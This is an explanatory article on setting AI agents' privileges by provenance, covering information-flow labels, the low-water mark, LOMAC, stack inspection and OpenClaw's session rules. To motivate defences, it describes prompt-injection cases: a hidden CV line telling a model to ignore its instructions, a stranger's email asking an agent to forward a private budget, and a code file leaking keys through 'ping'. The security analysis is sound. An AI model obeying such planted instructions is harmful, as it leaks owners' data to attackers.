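# Assigning AI agents' privileges by the provenance of the conversation

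## Sessions, sources and privileges: the background

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools it can act through, such as a shell, a mailbox or a code repository. The owner sets up the agent and controls its permissions, but the agent usually receives requests from other sources too, including group chats, timers the owner set weeks ago, and emails from strangers. Many systems decide what the agent may do in each case based on provenance, the record of where a message or piece of data came from and what it was derived from.

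A session is one running conversation with its own context. A trigger is the event that starts a session or a turn within it, such as an owner's message, a group message, a timer, an incoming email, or a webhook (a request sent automatically by another program). The simplest way to assign privileges is a session-origin rule, which fixes a session's privileges by who or what started it. For example, the owner's sessions might get access to the shell and the mailbox, while a stranger's sessions get neither. Such a rule is easy to build and explain, but it doesn't adjust privileges once the session is running, and a session that the owner opened may soon contain text that somebody else wrote. A content-tracking rule makes privileges depend on every source whose content has influenced the session or the action. Some operating systems applied the same idea before language models existed, by lowering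 a program's privilege after it had read untrusted input.

### How a turn works

The model only produces text, and an ordinary program around it, the runtime, does everything else. In *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, Bolin (2026) describes how this works in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. When a message arrives, the runtime assembles a prompt from standing instructions, definitions of the available tools, a description of the working environment and the message itself. Each item has a role (system, developer, user or assistant, from highest to lowest priority), which indicates how much weight its content should have. The model then returns either a final answer to the user, which ends the turn, or a request to call a tool, for instance to list the files in a folder. After a tool request, the runtime runs the tool, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again.

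Each new prompt in Codex begins with an exact copy of the previous one, and the next turn starts from the whole history, including earlier tool calls. A web page that the agent read in the morning is therefore still part of the model's input in the afternoon, when the owner asks for something unrelated. Once the conversation grows too long, Codex replaces it with a shorter list of items, so the page can still influence the model after its text is gone. Memory also carries content into other sessions. *SAFE-Mem* (2026) gives the example of an assistant that stores a line hidden in a web page and relies on it three weeks later.

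A tool call is only a request. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) point out in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that the application decides whether to execute it. Agent software commonly lets developers intervene at this point. Anthropic documents hooks that can intercept, modify or block a call before it runs. OpenClaw, a personal agent that people reach through messaging channels, lists a similar hook in its *Agent loop* documentation. Any rule about privileges that does not rely on the model's good behaviour has to act at this point or earlier, by withholding the tool.

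### Three questions about one action

When an agent is about to send a file, one can ask who started the session, whose content is now in the agent's context, and on whose authority it would send the file. People easily confuse these questions because in the simplest case, when an owner types a request and the agent carries it out, the answer to all three is the owner.

The runtime can determine who started the session once, when the trigger arrives, usually by checking an account or a phone number. The list of people whose content is in the context can grow with every tool result. Authority concerns what someone is allowed to do, which no log of events can establish. *Conflux* (Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, 2026) distinguishes influence, which is a fact about provenance, from authority, which is whatever the organisation's access-control system permits. In its example, Ava starts a session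 and asks an agent to update a customer record with the status given in a report that Ben wrote. Both Ava and Ben have influenced the update, because the value comes from Ben's report. Whether the update may go ahead depends on policy. The paper's own policy is strict and requires every principal who influenced an action to have permission to perform it. It defines a principal as any user or agent that can author information, including one with no permissions.

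*Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) draws the same distinctions in slightly different terms. It uses "grant" for the part of a user's authority that an agent receives for a task, and "approval" for an explicit confirmation that permits a sensitive operation or widens the grant. A retrieved document may supply facts for a report, and a trusted directory may supply the right recipient's address, but neither counts as approval to send the report to anyone else. *AIRGuard* (2026) checks this mechanically. Every record of authority names its issuer, and the system rejects any record whose issuer comes from a web page or a tool's output.

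A session-origin rule bases an agent's authority on who started the session. This is reasonable as long as that person is the only one whose content is in the context, or at least the only one who could want to misuse the agent.

Buckley and Schroeder de Witt argue that even a very good model cannot tell with certainty from the text and the user's request alone whether an action is authorised. In their example, a model receives exactly the same document and user request in two runs. A colleague with the right permissions wrote the document in the first run, and an attacker wrote it in the second. A deterministic defence that uses only the text and the request has no information about who wrote the document, so it must treat both runs the same way and either admit an unauthorised action or refuse an authorised one. A runtime can add the author's name to the prompt, but then the runtime supplies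 the missing fact, and the protection still depends on the model giving it the proper weight.

### Indirect prompt injection and the confused deputy

An attacker can influence a session without starting it or having any access to the assistant, by planting instructions in content that the agent will read while doing something else. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) named this indirect prompt injection and demonstrated it on real products, including Microsoft's Bing Chat, where invisible instructions on a web page could steer the assistant of a user who had that page open. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C (2025) for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives an everyday example. A recruiter asks a model to score CVs against a job's requirements, and one candidate has hidden a line in the CV telling the model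 to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate for interview.

Computer security has long called a program in this position a confused deputy. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler recorded usage statistics in a file in a system directory, so the staff had given it permission to write to any file there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The user didn't have permission to write to it, but the compiler did, so the operating system allowed the write and the billing information was lost.

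Hardy concluded that the compiler had authority from two sources, the user who invoked it and its own licence, and could not specify which one it was using for a given write. Tymshare first added a way to switch between the two, but some applications soon needed more than two. Hardy came to prefer capabilities, which are references that both identify a file and carry the right to use it. With capabilities, the user gives the compiler a capability for the output file, and a user without one for the billing file cannot direct output there.

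An agent working in its owner's session has the owner's authority, and a stranger's email can supply the file name. David C accepts the parallel with the Tymshare compiler but thinks the agent's case is worse. The compiler could be rewritten to keep its two authorities apart, whereas a language model does not distinguish instructions from data and only predicts the next token from all the text so far. He calls it "inherently confusable", doubts that anyone will ever fully solve prompt injection, and recommends limiting what the system around the model can do. One limit he passes on, from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that a model's privileges should drop to those of any party whose information it processes, which is the bluntest form of content-tracking rule.

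### Labels and how they combine

To apply such a rule, a system must track where data came from, even after the model has mixed data from different sources. Information-flow control does this by labelling data, carrying the labels through computation, and allowing or blocking actions based on the labels. An integrity label records how far the system trusts the data's source to influence actions, and a confidentiality label records who may receive the data.

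The central rule, from *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976), is that derived data takes the combined label of everything it came from. Whatever f does, a value computed as f(a₁, …, aₙ) gets the label a₁ ⊕ … ⊕ aₙ, where ⊕ is the combining operation. Denning argues that the combined label must be at least as restrictive as each of its parts, because if a system permitted the assignment c := a + b but forbade c := a, anyone could set b to zero and copy a by addition.

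Denning also distinguished explicit flows, where a program copies or computes with a value, from implicit flows, where the value only determines what the program does. If a program sets b to zero only when a is zero, anyone who sees b unchanged learns something about a, even though nothing was copied. Agents routinely produce implicit flows. For example, an email can influence which calendar entry an agent deletes, even if none of the email's words appear in the tool call.

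In the same paper, Denning described the choice between the two kinds of rule fifty years ago. A running process may take its security class from the clearance of the user who owns it, which corresponds to a session-origin rule, or from the history of the classes it has had access to, which corresponds to a content-tracking rule.

For agents, Costa and colleagues use two integrity labels, T for trusted and U for untrusted. Combining the two gives U (written T ⊔ U = U), so one untrusted input makes the result untrusted. An untrusted label that spreads this way to everything derived from the data is called taint. For confidentiality, they label data with the set of people who may read it, and they combine two labels by taking their intersection. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text based on both.

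A language model's reply could depend on any part of its prompt, so in the basic version Costa and colleagues give the reply the combined label of everything in the prompt. They acknowledge that this may be too cautious, since a given reply may not depend on the stranger's email. The practical drawback is that a single untrusted message taints whatever the agent does afterwards in that context.

### Reference monitors, endorsement and declassification

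Labels have no effect unless something checks them. A reference monitor is a component outside the model that checks every consequential action against a policy. A consequential action is a tool call with effects outside the conversation, such as sending, writing, scheduling or paying. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) argues for treating the model as an operating system treats an ordinary program, as untrusted and needing its requests checked. Every request must pass through the monitor, and attackers must not be able to alter the monitor or its policy. Even then, the outcome depends on what the policy permits. One attack the paper analyses involved Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, which asked for human approval before many shell commands but let the network command "ping" run without it. A malicious prompt in a code file could get the agent to read secret keys and send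 them out in the address that "ping" looked up.

Strict labels would also block much legitimate work, so practical systems allow exceptions. *Nonmalleable Information Flow* (2017) gives the standard terms for the two kinds: endorsement, which treats data as more trustworthy than its sources would warrant, and declassification, which releases data to someone its label would exclude. A trusted party should make both kinds of exception deliberately, because the labels would offer no protection if untrusted text could trigger them.

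Endorsing data differs from approving an action. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) describe a benign email with a to-do list of ten items, each of which needs a consequential tool call. If the owner endorses the email, the agent can carry out all ten after one question; otherwise, the owner must approve each call separately. But endorsing the email also means vouching for all of it, including any line the owner failed to notice. Kolluri and colleagues left declassification out of their agent because they judged that whether to release private information depends too much on the situation for a blanket decision.

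### A summary of the inbox

Suppose Maya owns an agent and asks it to summarise her inbox, which holds one email from her colleague Tom and one from a stranger. Only Maya and Tom may read the file budget.xlsx. The stranger's email contains a hidden line asking the agent to forward that file to the stranger's address, and the model tries to comply.

Each label below gives integrity first and permitted readers second. Maya's employer counts mail from staff as trusted, which is a policy choice. The content-tracking rule has two conditions, both taken from Costa and colleagues. A consequential call must come from a trusted context with trusted arguments, and data may go only to its permitted readers.

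| Step | Labels | Session-origin rule | Content-tracking rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Maya asks for a summary | Context: (T, everyone) | Gives the session Maya's privileges | Leaves consequential actions open |
| The agent calls the tool that reads the inbox | Call: (T, everyone) | Allows | Allows |
| Tom's email enters | Email: (T, {Maya, Tom}). Context: (T, {Maya, Tom}) | No change | Text based on the context may go only to Maya and Tom |
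| The stranger's email enters | Email: (U, {Maya, stranger}). Context: (U, {Maya}) | No change | Closes consequential actions |
| The agent proposes to forward budget.xlsx to the stranger | Call: (U, {Maya}). File: (T, {Maya, Tom}) | Allows | Blocks |
| The agent shows Maya the summary | Summary: (U, {Maya}) | Allows | Allows |

The context label in the fourth row follows from the combining rule. For integrity, T ⊔ U = U. For readers, the intersection of {Maya, Tom} and {Maya, stranger} is {Maya}. The forwarding call fails both conditions, since the model produced it in an untrusted context and the stranger is not a permitted reader of the budget. Under the session-origin rule the call succeeds, because Maya started the session and may forward her own files. Maya gets her summary under either rule. The stranger may have influenced its wording, so its U label is a reason to read it with some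 care.

If the stranger's email had opened a new session on arrival, a session-origin rule would have given that session a stranger's privileges and also blocked the forwarding. The rule fails only when untrusted text enters a session that had a trusted start. If the hidden line had asked the agent to forward the budget to Tom, the call would have met the readers condition, and only the integrity condition would have stopped it. Costa and colleagues note that, in general, a readers condition alone does not prevent prompt injection but does limit the damage.

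The content-tracking rule can also block actions that Maya explicitly requested. Suppose she asks the agent, in one message, to summarize her inbox and send the budget to Tom. If the agent reads the inbox first, the context is untrusted by the time it proposes to send the file, and the rule blocks the call. The agent could send the file first, while the context is still (T, everyone). It could also ask Maya to approve the call or to endorse the stranger's email, though endorsing the email would be a mistake here. But people who have to confirm everything tire of it and stop reading the requests.

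The rule in Buckley and Schroeder de Witt's *Conflux* would give the same result for the stranger. It records everyone who influenced the call (Maya, Tom and the stranger) and checks whether each of them may forward the budget. If Tom's were the only other email in the inbox, a two-valued label would treat him as trusted, but the rule would still check what Tom himself may do. The paper's proof that no unauthorised action gets through assumes, among other things, an accurate record of every input that influenced the model.

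### AgentDojo

Much of the evidence on such designs comes from *AgentDojo*, a benchmark introduced by Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024). It simulates an office workspace, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank, with working tools and invented data. The first version has 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill, and 27 injection tasks, which are attackers' goals, such as sending money to their own account. Pairing every user task with every injection task in the same setting yields 629 security cases. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent solves when nobody attacks. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which it solves the user's task without adversarial side effects, and the targeted attack success rate is the share in which the attacker's goal is met. Ordinary code checks these results from the agent's output and the state of the simulated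 accounts and mailboxes, because the same injection might also manipulate a language model acting as judge. An agent that refused every request would have an attack success rate of zero, so that rate means little without the utility figures. The benchmark has since grown to more than 900 pairings, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), and results from different versions are not strictly comparable. In every security case the user opens the session and the attacker's text arrives later through a tool, so a rule based only on who started the session would treat every case as the user's own work.

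## Earlier systems that lowered privilege after untrusted input

Designers of operating systems and language runtimes had to choose between session-origin and content-tracking rules long before agents existed. A process (one running copy of a program) may start under a trusted user and then read a file that somebody else wrote. Some designers fixed a process's privileges at the start, and others lowered them as it ran. Both approaches had problems that agent developers now face.

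### The low-water mark

In the 1970s, K. J. Biba proposed several ways to protect the integrity of data on military computers. Each process and each file has an integrity level. Under his low-water-mark rule, a process s that reads an object o drops to the lower of the two levels, which course slides from Purdue University write as:

i(s) ← min(i(s), i(o))

The process may then write only to objects at or below its new level. Low-integrity data can't reach a higher-level file through any chain of reads and writes, because the level of each process in the chain drops before it writes.

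Biba also described a ring policy, which never changes a process's level and lets it read anything. It limits only what the process may write. According to the Purdue University slides, the policy relies on processes to handle their inputs correctly. A session-origin rule relies on the agent in the same way.

Under the low-water mark, a process can lose the right to write its own output, which is called the self-revocation problem. Suppose a process at level 1 opens report.txt, also at level 1, to hold its results. It then reads prices.csv, a level-0 file from the internet, and its own level drops to min(1, 0) = 0. When it tries to save the results, the system refuses because report.txt is now at a higher level than the process. Only a new process can regain the right to write to the file. Stony Brook University's Secure Systems Lab points out in *Self-revocation Free Downgrading (SRFD)*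 that programmers don't write applications to handle such failures. Maya's agent ran into the same problem when it read her inbox and lost the right to send the budget.

### LOMAC

Tim Fraser built the low-water mark into Linux as LOMAC, a module with two levels, high and low. Fraser (2000) recounted in the mailing-list post *LWM* that self-revocation soon broke everyday commands. Typing "ps auxw | less" should list the running processes one screen at a time, with the program "ps" passing its list to "less" through a pipe. But "ps" read some low-level system files, so LOMAC demoted it and it could no longer write to the high-level pipe, which left "less" with nothing to show. To fix this, Fraser treated all the processes in one job as a single subject, so "less" was demoted along with "ps" and the pipe between them kept working. The fix worked for commands typed at a shell but caused trouble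 with some timer-started jobs. It also didn't help the process with the report, which still couldn't write to a high-level file after its demotion.

The Stony Brook lab later moved the refusal earlier. Its system tracks the actual flow of information between processes and files, and refuses to open a low-level file if reading it would lead to self-revocation. Programs generally cope better with a file that won't open than with a write that fails halfway through. This approach would be harder to implement in an agent's runtime, because a process's open files give some indication of what it may write, whereas a model may first request a tool long after reading the email that rules it out.

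LOMAC gave users different privileges at login without keeping a list of trusted users. Fraser (2001), in *LOMAC*, explains that when someone logged in at the machine's own console, the shell started at the high level, and that an ordinary user's shell then dropped at once because it read settings from a low-level home directory. The administrator's home directory was high-level, so the administrator's shell stayed high until it read something low. A session-origin rule would also give users different privileges at login, but LOMAC did this by tracking what each shell read, and it kept tracking afterwards. It also treated the network as a low-level file, so a server dropped as soon as its first message arrived.

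Some programs couldn't work under these conditions. The system logger has to copy messages from low-level processes into a high-level file, and remote administration requires a high-level process that reads from the network. Fraser exempted a short list of programs from demotion, including the logger and the remote-login server sshd, and accepted that LOMAC would not contain an attacker who took over one of them at the high level. He also supplied a tool that let an administrator copy a downloaded file to the high-level area after checking it, a step now called endorsement.

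LOMAC added about 3 percent to the time needed to build a Linux kernel. Fraser once reinstalled it on his chief scientist's workstation and forgot to tell him, and the scientist, who was using the machine only lightly, didn't notice for 11 days. A three-level version protected more of users' own files, but it forced people to run separate text editors for files at different levels, and Fraser left it out of the later prototype. LOMAC also had an enforcement gap, because a process could map a file into its memory and change it there without making any request that LOMAC could check. The version in FreeBSD's *mac_lomac* can revoke such mappings when it demotes a process.

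A system with only two levels can't represent a file that is open to one colleague and closed to another. In *Trojan Horse Resistant Discretionary Access Control*, Mao, Li and colleagues replaced the level with a set of everyone who might have influenced the process, counting the whole network as one member. They argued that ordinary file permissions are an adequate policy, and that the weakness is the assumption that a single principal is responsible for each request. In their Linux system, a request succeeds only if the file's permissions allow it for every member of the set. *Conflux* applies much the same condition to agents.

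### The call stack and the execution history

Language runtimes had a related problem with code from several sources. A program might combine a trusted library that had the right to delete files with an applet, a small program from an unknown website, that lacked it. Java and Microsoft's .NET runtime handled this with stack inspection, which checked the call stack, a list of the code that has been called and hasn't yet returned. Each piece of code had static rights, usually based on where it came from, and a request succeeded only if every piece of code on the stack had the necessary right. An applet therefore couldn't delete a file by calling the library, which prevented one form of the confused deputy problem. Trusted code could override the check for a particular operation.

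Abadi and Fournet (2003), in *Access Control based on Execution History*, objected that stack inspection protects code from its callers but leaves callers exposed to the code they call. If A calls B, B returns, and A then calls C, B is no longer on the stack, even though its result may determine what C does. In one of their examples, a trusted program asks an untrusted plug-in for the name of a temporary file to delete, and the plug-in returns the name of the password file, which the program then deletes.

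| Step | Code on the stack | Rights under stack inspection | Rights under the history-based rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| The program starts | Program | All | All |
| The program calls the plug-in | Program, plug-in | No file rights | No file rights |
| The plug-in returns the name of the password file | Program | All | No file rights |
| The program asks the library to delete that file | Program, library | Deletion succeeds | Deletion fails |

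The program could check the name before using it. Abadi and Fournet considered this impractical as a general solution, because the caller may be an old library function whose author never thought about security, and because it can be hard to tell before run time which code a call will reach.

The last column shows their alternative, the history-based rule. The runtime stores the program's current rights in a variable, D. Whenever code c with static rights S(c) runs, the runtime sets D ← D ∩ S(c), so that only the rights in both sets remain. The lost rights do not come back when c returns. Security-aware code can recover them with the Accept operation, which runs a block of less trusted code and then restores some or all of the rights held before it. The programmer who uses Accept is responsible for checking the result first.

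Placing an Accept around every call to less trusted code would reproduce stack inspection. When a programmer forgets about security, the program may delete the wrong file under stack inspection, while under the history-based rule it stops with an error. But the history-based rule may also stop code that has proper authorization, as Pistoia, Banerjee and Naumann pointed out.

A session-origin rule checks the caller, much as stack inspection does. It protects the agent's tools from a stranger who opens a session, but not from a web page that the agent fetched earlier in the owner's session. A content-tracking rule checks the history. The case for checking history is stronger for agents than for Java programs, because a Java program may discard what a plug-in returned, while an agent's runtime normally puts the page into every later prompt.

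Abadi and Fournet's rule only partly carries over to agents, because it tracks which code has run and ignores where data came from. If a trusted program reads a file that untrusted code wrote last week, the program keeps the same rights. Since a web page or an email can steer an agent without being code, an agent's history has to record what the agent has read, as LOMAC did for processes.

### Noninterference as the test of soundness

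To say whether any of these rules is sound, one needs a definition of influence. Goguen and Meseguer supplied the standard one, noninterference, in 1982. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does affects what the second group can see. For integrity, the first group is the untrusted sources, and the things they must not affect are the protected actions. Let A(t, u) be the sequence of protected actions that a system takes on trusted input t and untrusted input u. The requirement is that

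A(t, u) = A(t, u′) for all t, u and u′.

A rule is sound if every program running under it meets this condition, including a program that an attacker controls.

A session-origin rule fails this test in Maya's inbox example, because her request stays the same while the stranger's text decides whether the agent forwards the budget. The low-water mark does much better. A process can make protected writes only before its first untrusted read, when it has received only trusted input, so the contents of the untrusted file can't affect those writes. This argument doesn't cover exempt programs such as LOMAC's logger, and it assumes that outsiders can't affect whether the untrusted read happens. If a process reads mail only when mail has arrived, a stranger can take away its rights by sending a message. Strictly, that is interference too, but it can only prevent protected actions, not cause them.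 For Maya, failing to send the budget is less harmful than leaking it to a stranger.

### Implicit flows

Demoting a whole process is crude, and designers have often wanted to label individual pieces of data instead. This is harder than it looks because of the implicit flows that Denning described. Consider two lines of a program that reads a stranger's email:

```
delete := false
if email = "yes" then delete := true
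```

The program doesn't copy any of the email into the variable "delete", so a tracker that follows only copying will treat the variable as trusted. A more careful tracker would taint any variable set inside a branch that depends on untrusted data. This works if the email says "yes". Otherwise, the program skips the assignment, so the tracker taints nothing and "delete" keeps a trusted label even though the stranger decided its value. A later line that acts only when "delete" is false would then act on the stranger's choice.

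In 1977, Denning and Denning proposed solving this by checking the program before it runs. A compiler can read both branches, including the one that a given run will skip. It rejects the program unless information with the condition's label is allowed to flow to every variable that either branch sets. Here, "delete" would need an untrusted label from the start, whatever the email said.

### Label creep

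Cautious tracking has its own drawback, called label creep. Labels combine easily and almost never separate, so more and more data is marked untrusted over time, until the marks no longer distinguish anything. This can happen quickly in a variant of the low-water mark that lowers the level of files as well as processes. If a process reads a low-level file and then adds a line to a shared log, the log's level drops. Every process that later reads the log drops too, along with whatever it writes next.

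Partly for this reason, Abadi and Fournet judged full information-flow control too restrictive for general-purpose runtimes and settled for tracking code. In *Towards more usable information flow policies for contemporary operating systems*, Sze, Mital and Sekar (2014) observed that mainstream operating systems, too, had adopted few advances in information-flow control, because strict enforcement limits what a system can do.

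Mao and colleagues considered whether their own system would eventually sink to the lowest integrity level, since its processes can never regain integrity once they lose it. They concluded that it would not, because the first process on the machine stays clean and keeps starting new clean ones. The permissions on important files also stop contaminated processes from writing to them.

An agent that works in one long context has no such fresh processes. Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, examined four personal agents, including OpenClaw, and found that all of them let successive tools share a single context without deliberately isolating them from each other. They think agents could run each skill, a packaged set of instructions for a task, in a fresh context with narrow permissions. That would limit label creep as short-lived processes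 do, provided the result passed back to the main context kept its label.

### Methods that depend on knowing the program

The low-water mark works without knowledge of the program it restricts. LOMAC could not distinguish a process that had read bad data and still worked properly from one that an attacker had taken over, so it demoted both. The same approach suits a language model, whose inner workings are at least as hard to judge from outside.

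Denning and Denning's check, however, needs a program whose branches a compiler can analyse. A language model has no line of code that tests whether the email contains "yes". It performs broadly the same arithmetic on every prompt, and its trained weights determine the output. Analysing that arithmetic would show only that the reply may depend on every word of the prompt, so the check would be no better than giving the reply the combined label of everything in the context.

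*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests, among other things, measuring an input's influence by removing or altering it and observing how the distribution of the agent's actions changes. This amounts to testing the noninterference condition by experiment. The test can reveal interference but can't rule it out, because no number of trials covers every text an attacker might write.

Exemptions also depend on knowing what the program should do. Fraser could exempt the system logger because it does one fixed job, and a programmer who knows what a proper result looks like can check a plug-in's result and then use Accept. A model's behavior is much harder to predict. Pirch and colleagues note that the same skill can lead to different tool calls depending on the context, the model and the task. A small conventional program that reads a stranger's email and passes on only a date is a better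 candidate for an exemption. A reviewer can confirm from its code that nothing else gets through, although the stranger still chooses the date.

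## OpenClaw: privileges set by who opened the conversation

OpenClaw is an open-source personal agent that runs on its owner's machine and answers through WhatsApp, Telegram, Slack and similar services. IMDA, Singapore's media and technology regulator, attributes its popularity largely to how easily it works out of the box, with access to local files, messaging services and long-term memory. IMDA also warns that its built-in security controls are limited. The agent's privileges depend mostly on who sent the message and which session it entered, so OpenClaw is the clearest deployed case of a session-origin rule, though it applies some checks to single turns rather than whole sessions. Its documentation changes often, so the settings below are those of September 2026 unless another month is given.

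### The route of a message

Messages from every channel go to one program, the gateway, which checks the sender, chooses a session and applies the tool policy before the model receives anything.

OpenClaw's *Access control and allowlists* describes pairing as the default for direct messages. An unknown sender receives a code, and the gateway ignores their messages until the owner approves the code. Codes expire after an hour, and each channel can have at most three pending requests. Approval adds the sender to a stored allowlist. The owner can instead admit only people already on an allowlist, open the agent to everyone, or turn direct messages off.

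The gateway applies two checks to group messages. It first consults its group allowlists, which can restrict both the groups it accepts and the members who may trigger the agent there. It then applies the mention gate, which filters out messages that don't address the agent by name. A reply to one of the agent's messages counts as a mention but doesn't get an excluded member past the allowlist. Since anyone in a room can type the agent's name, the mention gate controls when the agent responds but doesn't protect against a hostile member.

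OpenClaw then assigns the message to a session. By default, all direct messages go to the agent's main session so that a conversation can continue across devices and channels. Each group has its own session, and in May 2026 OpenClaw also gave each Telegram forum topic its own.

The tool policy then determines which tools the model can request. Rules can apply to the whole gateway, a model provider, an agent or a sandbox, and each layer can only remove tools that the others allow. The owner can also set the available tools by sender. Whatever the configuration, only the owner can use "cron" and "gateway" in chat, according to OpenClaw's *Hardened baselines*. "Cron" schedules jobs, and "gateway" acts on the gateway itself. Reserving them is sensible because both can have effects that outlast the conversation.

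Finally, the sandbox setting determines where commands run. In May 2026, OpenClaw documented three modes. With sandboxing off, everything runs on the host, the machine that runs the gateway. The "all" mode sandboxes every session, and "non-main" sandboxes every session except the main one. OpenClaw uses a session's key to decide whether it is non-main, so a group session counts as non-main even when the owner is speaking. An "elevated" setting lets chosen commands run outside the sandbox.

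In April 2026, OpenClaw recommended combining these pieces for an owner with private direct messages and public groups. Direct messages get full tools on the host, while groups get restricted tools in a sandbox. Both still use the same agent, workspace and memory.

The table shows the defaults for each origin. The heartbeat row describes October 2026.

| Origin | Session it enters | Tools | Where commands run |
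|---|---|---|---|
| Owner's direct message | Main | Everything the agent's policy allows, including "cron" and "gateway" | Host |
| Another paired contact | Main, shared with the owner | The same, without "cron" and "gateway" | Host |
| Group chat | One session per group | Depends on the sender; only the owner can use "cron" and "gateway" | Host, or a sandbox in "non-main" mode |
| Heartbeat | Main | The agent's ordinary tools | Host |
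| Scheduled job | The conversation that created it, a fresh session or main | If the agent created it, at most the tools of that turn; if the owner did, unrestricted unless the owner sets a list | Host; jobs that only run a command always use the host |
| Webhook | Main for a "wake" request, a fresh session for an "agent" request | The target agent's tools | Host |
| Email through the Gmail preset | One session per message | The default agent's tools | Host |

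Almost every row has the same value in the last column because sandboxing is off by default. If an owner only installs OpenClaw and pairs a few contacts, sessions will differ from one another, but their privileges will differ only slightly.

### Timers

A heartbeat is a turn that the gateway starts at regular intervals so that the agent can report anything that needs attention. As of October 2026, OpenClaw's *Heartbeat* gave the default interval as 30 minutes, or an hour with some kinds of Anthropic login. The heartbeat runs in the main session, and its prompt arrives as a user message. Nobody outside can start a heartbeat, so its trigger is about as trustworthy as a trigger can be. But the model also receives the history of the main session, including whatever paired contacts have written there.

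The default prompt tells the agent not to infer or repeat old tasks from earlier chats, but the runtime doesn't enforce this. An owner can enforce separation with a setting that gives every heartbeat a fresh session. OpenClaw may also be phasing out heartbeats for monitoring. By late November 2026, its *Automations* directed owners to a guide for moving periodic monitoring into ordinary scheduled jobs.

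Scheduled jobs have a more careful rule. When the agent creates a job, the gateway stores a list of the tools available in that turn as a cap on the job, and the agent can't widen the list later. Without the cap, an agent with few tools in one turn could gain more by scheduling a job. OpenClaw's *Automation payloads* explains that jobs created by an authenticated operator are unrestricted unless the operator names the tools.

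The cap preserves the privileges of the creating turn, but it doesn't record whose text led to the job. Suppose Maya asks her OpenClaw agent to go through her mail, and the agent schedules a task because of a line in a stranger's email. The turn belongs to Maya, so the agent has "cron", and the new job inherits her tools. The job can run when she is away. Attacks through stored content exploit this kind of delay.

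A job created in a conversation normally belongs to that conversation. It runs separately, but reads a limited stretch of the conversation's recent messages and posts its answer back there. If a job's command needs approval and the owner chooses "Always allow", later runs that the approval covers don't need the owner's approval again, even though the agent may have read different material by then.

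### Webhooks and email

Webhooks are off by default, and every request must carry a secret token. OpenClaw's *Inbound webhooks* describes two main kinds of request. A "wake" request places a short text in the main session as a trusted system event. An "agent" request starts a turn in a fresh session and wraps the text in markers that identify it as external. By October 2026, an immediate wake joined the session's ordinary message queue and ran with that session's current permissions.

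The token authenticates the service that delivered the request, not the author of the text inside it. A company's support system, for example, may use a valid token to forward a customer's complaint word for word. The maintainers therefore tell owners to use "wake" only for short notifications that the owners control, and OpenClaw's *Prompt injection* classes webhook contents as untrusted even when the delivering system belongs to the owner.

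Wrapping is the closest thing OpenClaw has to an integrity label. The gateway adds the markers and strips out special strings that some self-hosted models would otherwise read as the start of a system or assistant message. But the label is there for the model to read, and no reference monitor checks it before a tool call runs. According to OpenClaw, wrapping leaves the tools and the workspace available.

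The same gap is clearer with email. The built-in Gmail preset opens a separate session for each message, which keeps one stranger's text out of another's conversation. But according to OpenClaw's *Gmail PubSub triggers*, that session runs as the default agent, with its usual tools and workspace, unless the owner configures another agent. Maya therefore has to lower the session's privileges herself.

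The maintainers recommend a dedicated reader agent for this. It works in a sandbox without access to the owner's workspace, and its only permitted tool reports the session's status. The configuration explicitly denies it the shell, files, the web, the browser, "cron" and "gateway". The maintainers also describe a test in which the owner sends an email from another account with a harmless instruction to follow a link and run a command, then inspects the transcript. Any attempt to follow the link or run something counts as a failure of the boundary, so the test catches a configuration that would have let a more careful attacker through.

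Even when a webhook session is isolated, the default settings allow a completion event in the target agent's main session if an "agent" request specifies no destination for its answer. The reader configuration turns this off.

### Who may trigger the agent, and whose text it reads

OpenClaw separates trigger authorization from context visibility. Trigger authorization is about who can start a turn, which the pairing list, group allowlists and mention gates control. Context visibility is about what other text the model receives with the message, such as a quoted reply or earlier messages in a thread. Someone who isn't allowed to trigger the agent may still have written much of that text.

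The contextVisibility setting controls which additional text is kept. Its default, "all", keeps everything as received. "allowlist" keeps only text from senders who pass the active allowlist checks, and "allowlist_quote" also keeps one explicitly quoted reply.

Suppose Maya adds her agent to a group and allows only herself to trigger it. Another member posts a message containing a planted instruction. The gateway doesn't start a turn, because that member isn't allowed to trigger the agent. Later, Maya replies to the message, mentions the agent and asks for a summary of the discussion. She passes every check, so the turn runs with her tools, and under the default setting the planted instruction reaches the model as quoted text.

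OpenClaw's maintainers write that sender checks apply only to the person who requested the current turn. The checks don't authenticate or clean anything else in the prompt, including fetched pages, attachments and tool results. "Content from another person can therefore influence an owner-triggered turn," the maintainers conclude. Session-origin rules in general have this weakness.

Setting contextVisibility to "allowlist" would remove the quoted message in Maya's group. But the setting filters only text that the messaging channel supplies, not web pages that the agent opens during the turn. It also filters by who posted a text rather than who wrote it, so if Tom is on the allowlist and pastes a stranger's message into the chat, the filter treats the words as Tom's.

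### Defaults that weaken the tiers

The shared main session weakens the distinction between the owner and a paired contact more than anything else does. Say Tom has paired with Maya's agent and asks it on Monday to schedule a daily export of her calendar. The agent can't comply because Tom's turn lacks "cron", but his request stays in the history. On Tuesday Maya asks for something unrelated. The agent now has "cron", Tom's request is still in its context, and whether it acts on that request depends on the model.

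Stack inspection in Java had the same flaw. The low-water mark would have kept Maya's session at the lower level until she opened a new one. That would be a serious drawback for a personal assistant, since after a single message from Tom she would lose "cron" in the conversation she uses for everything.

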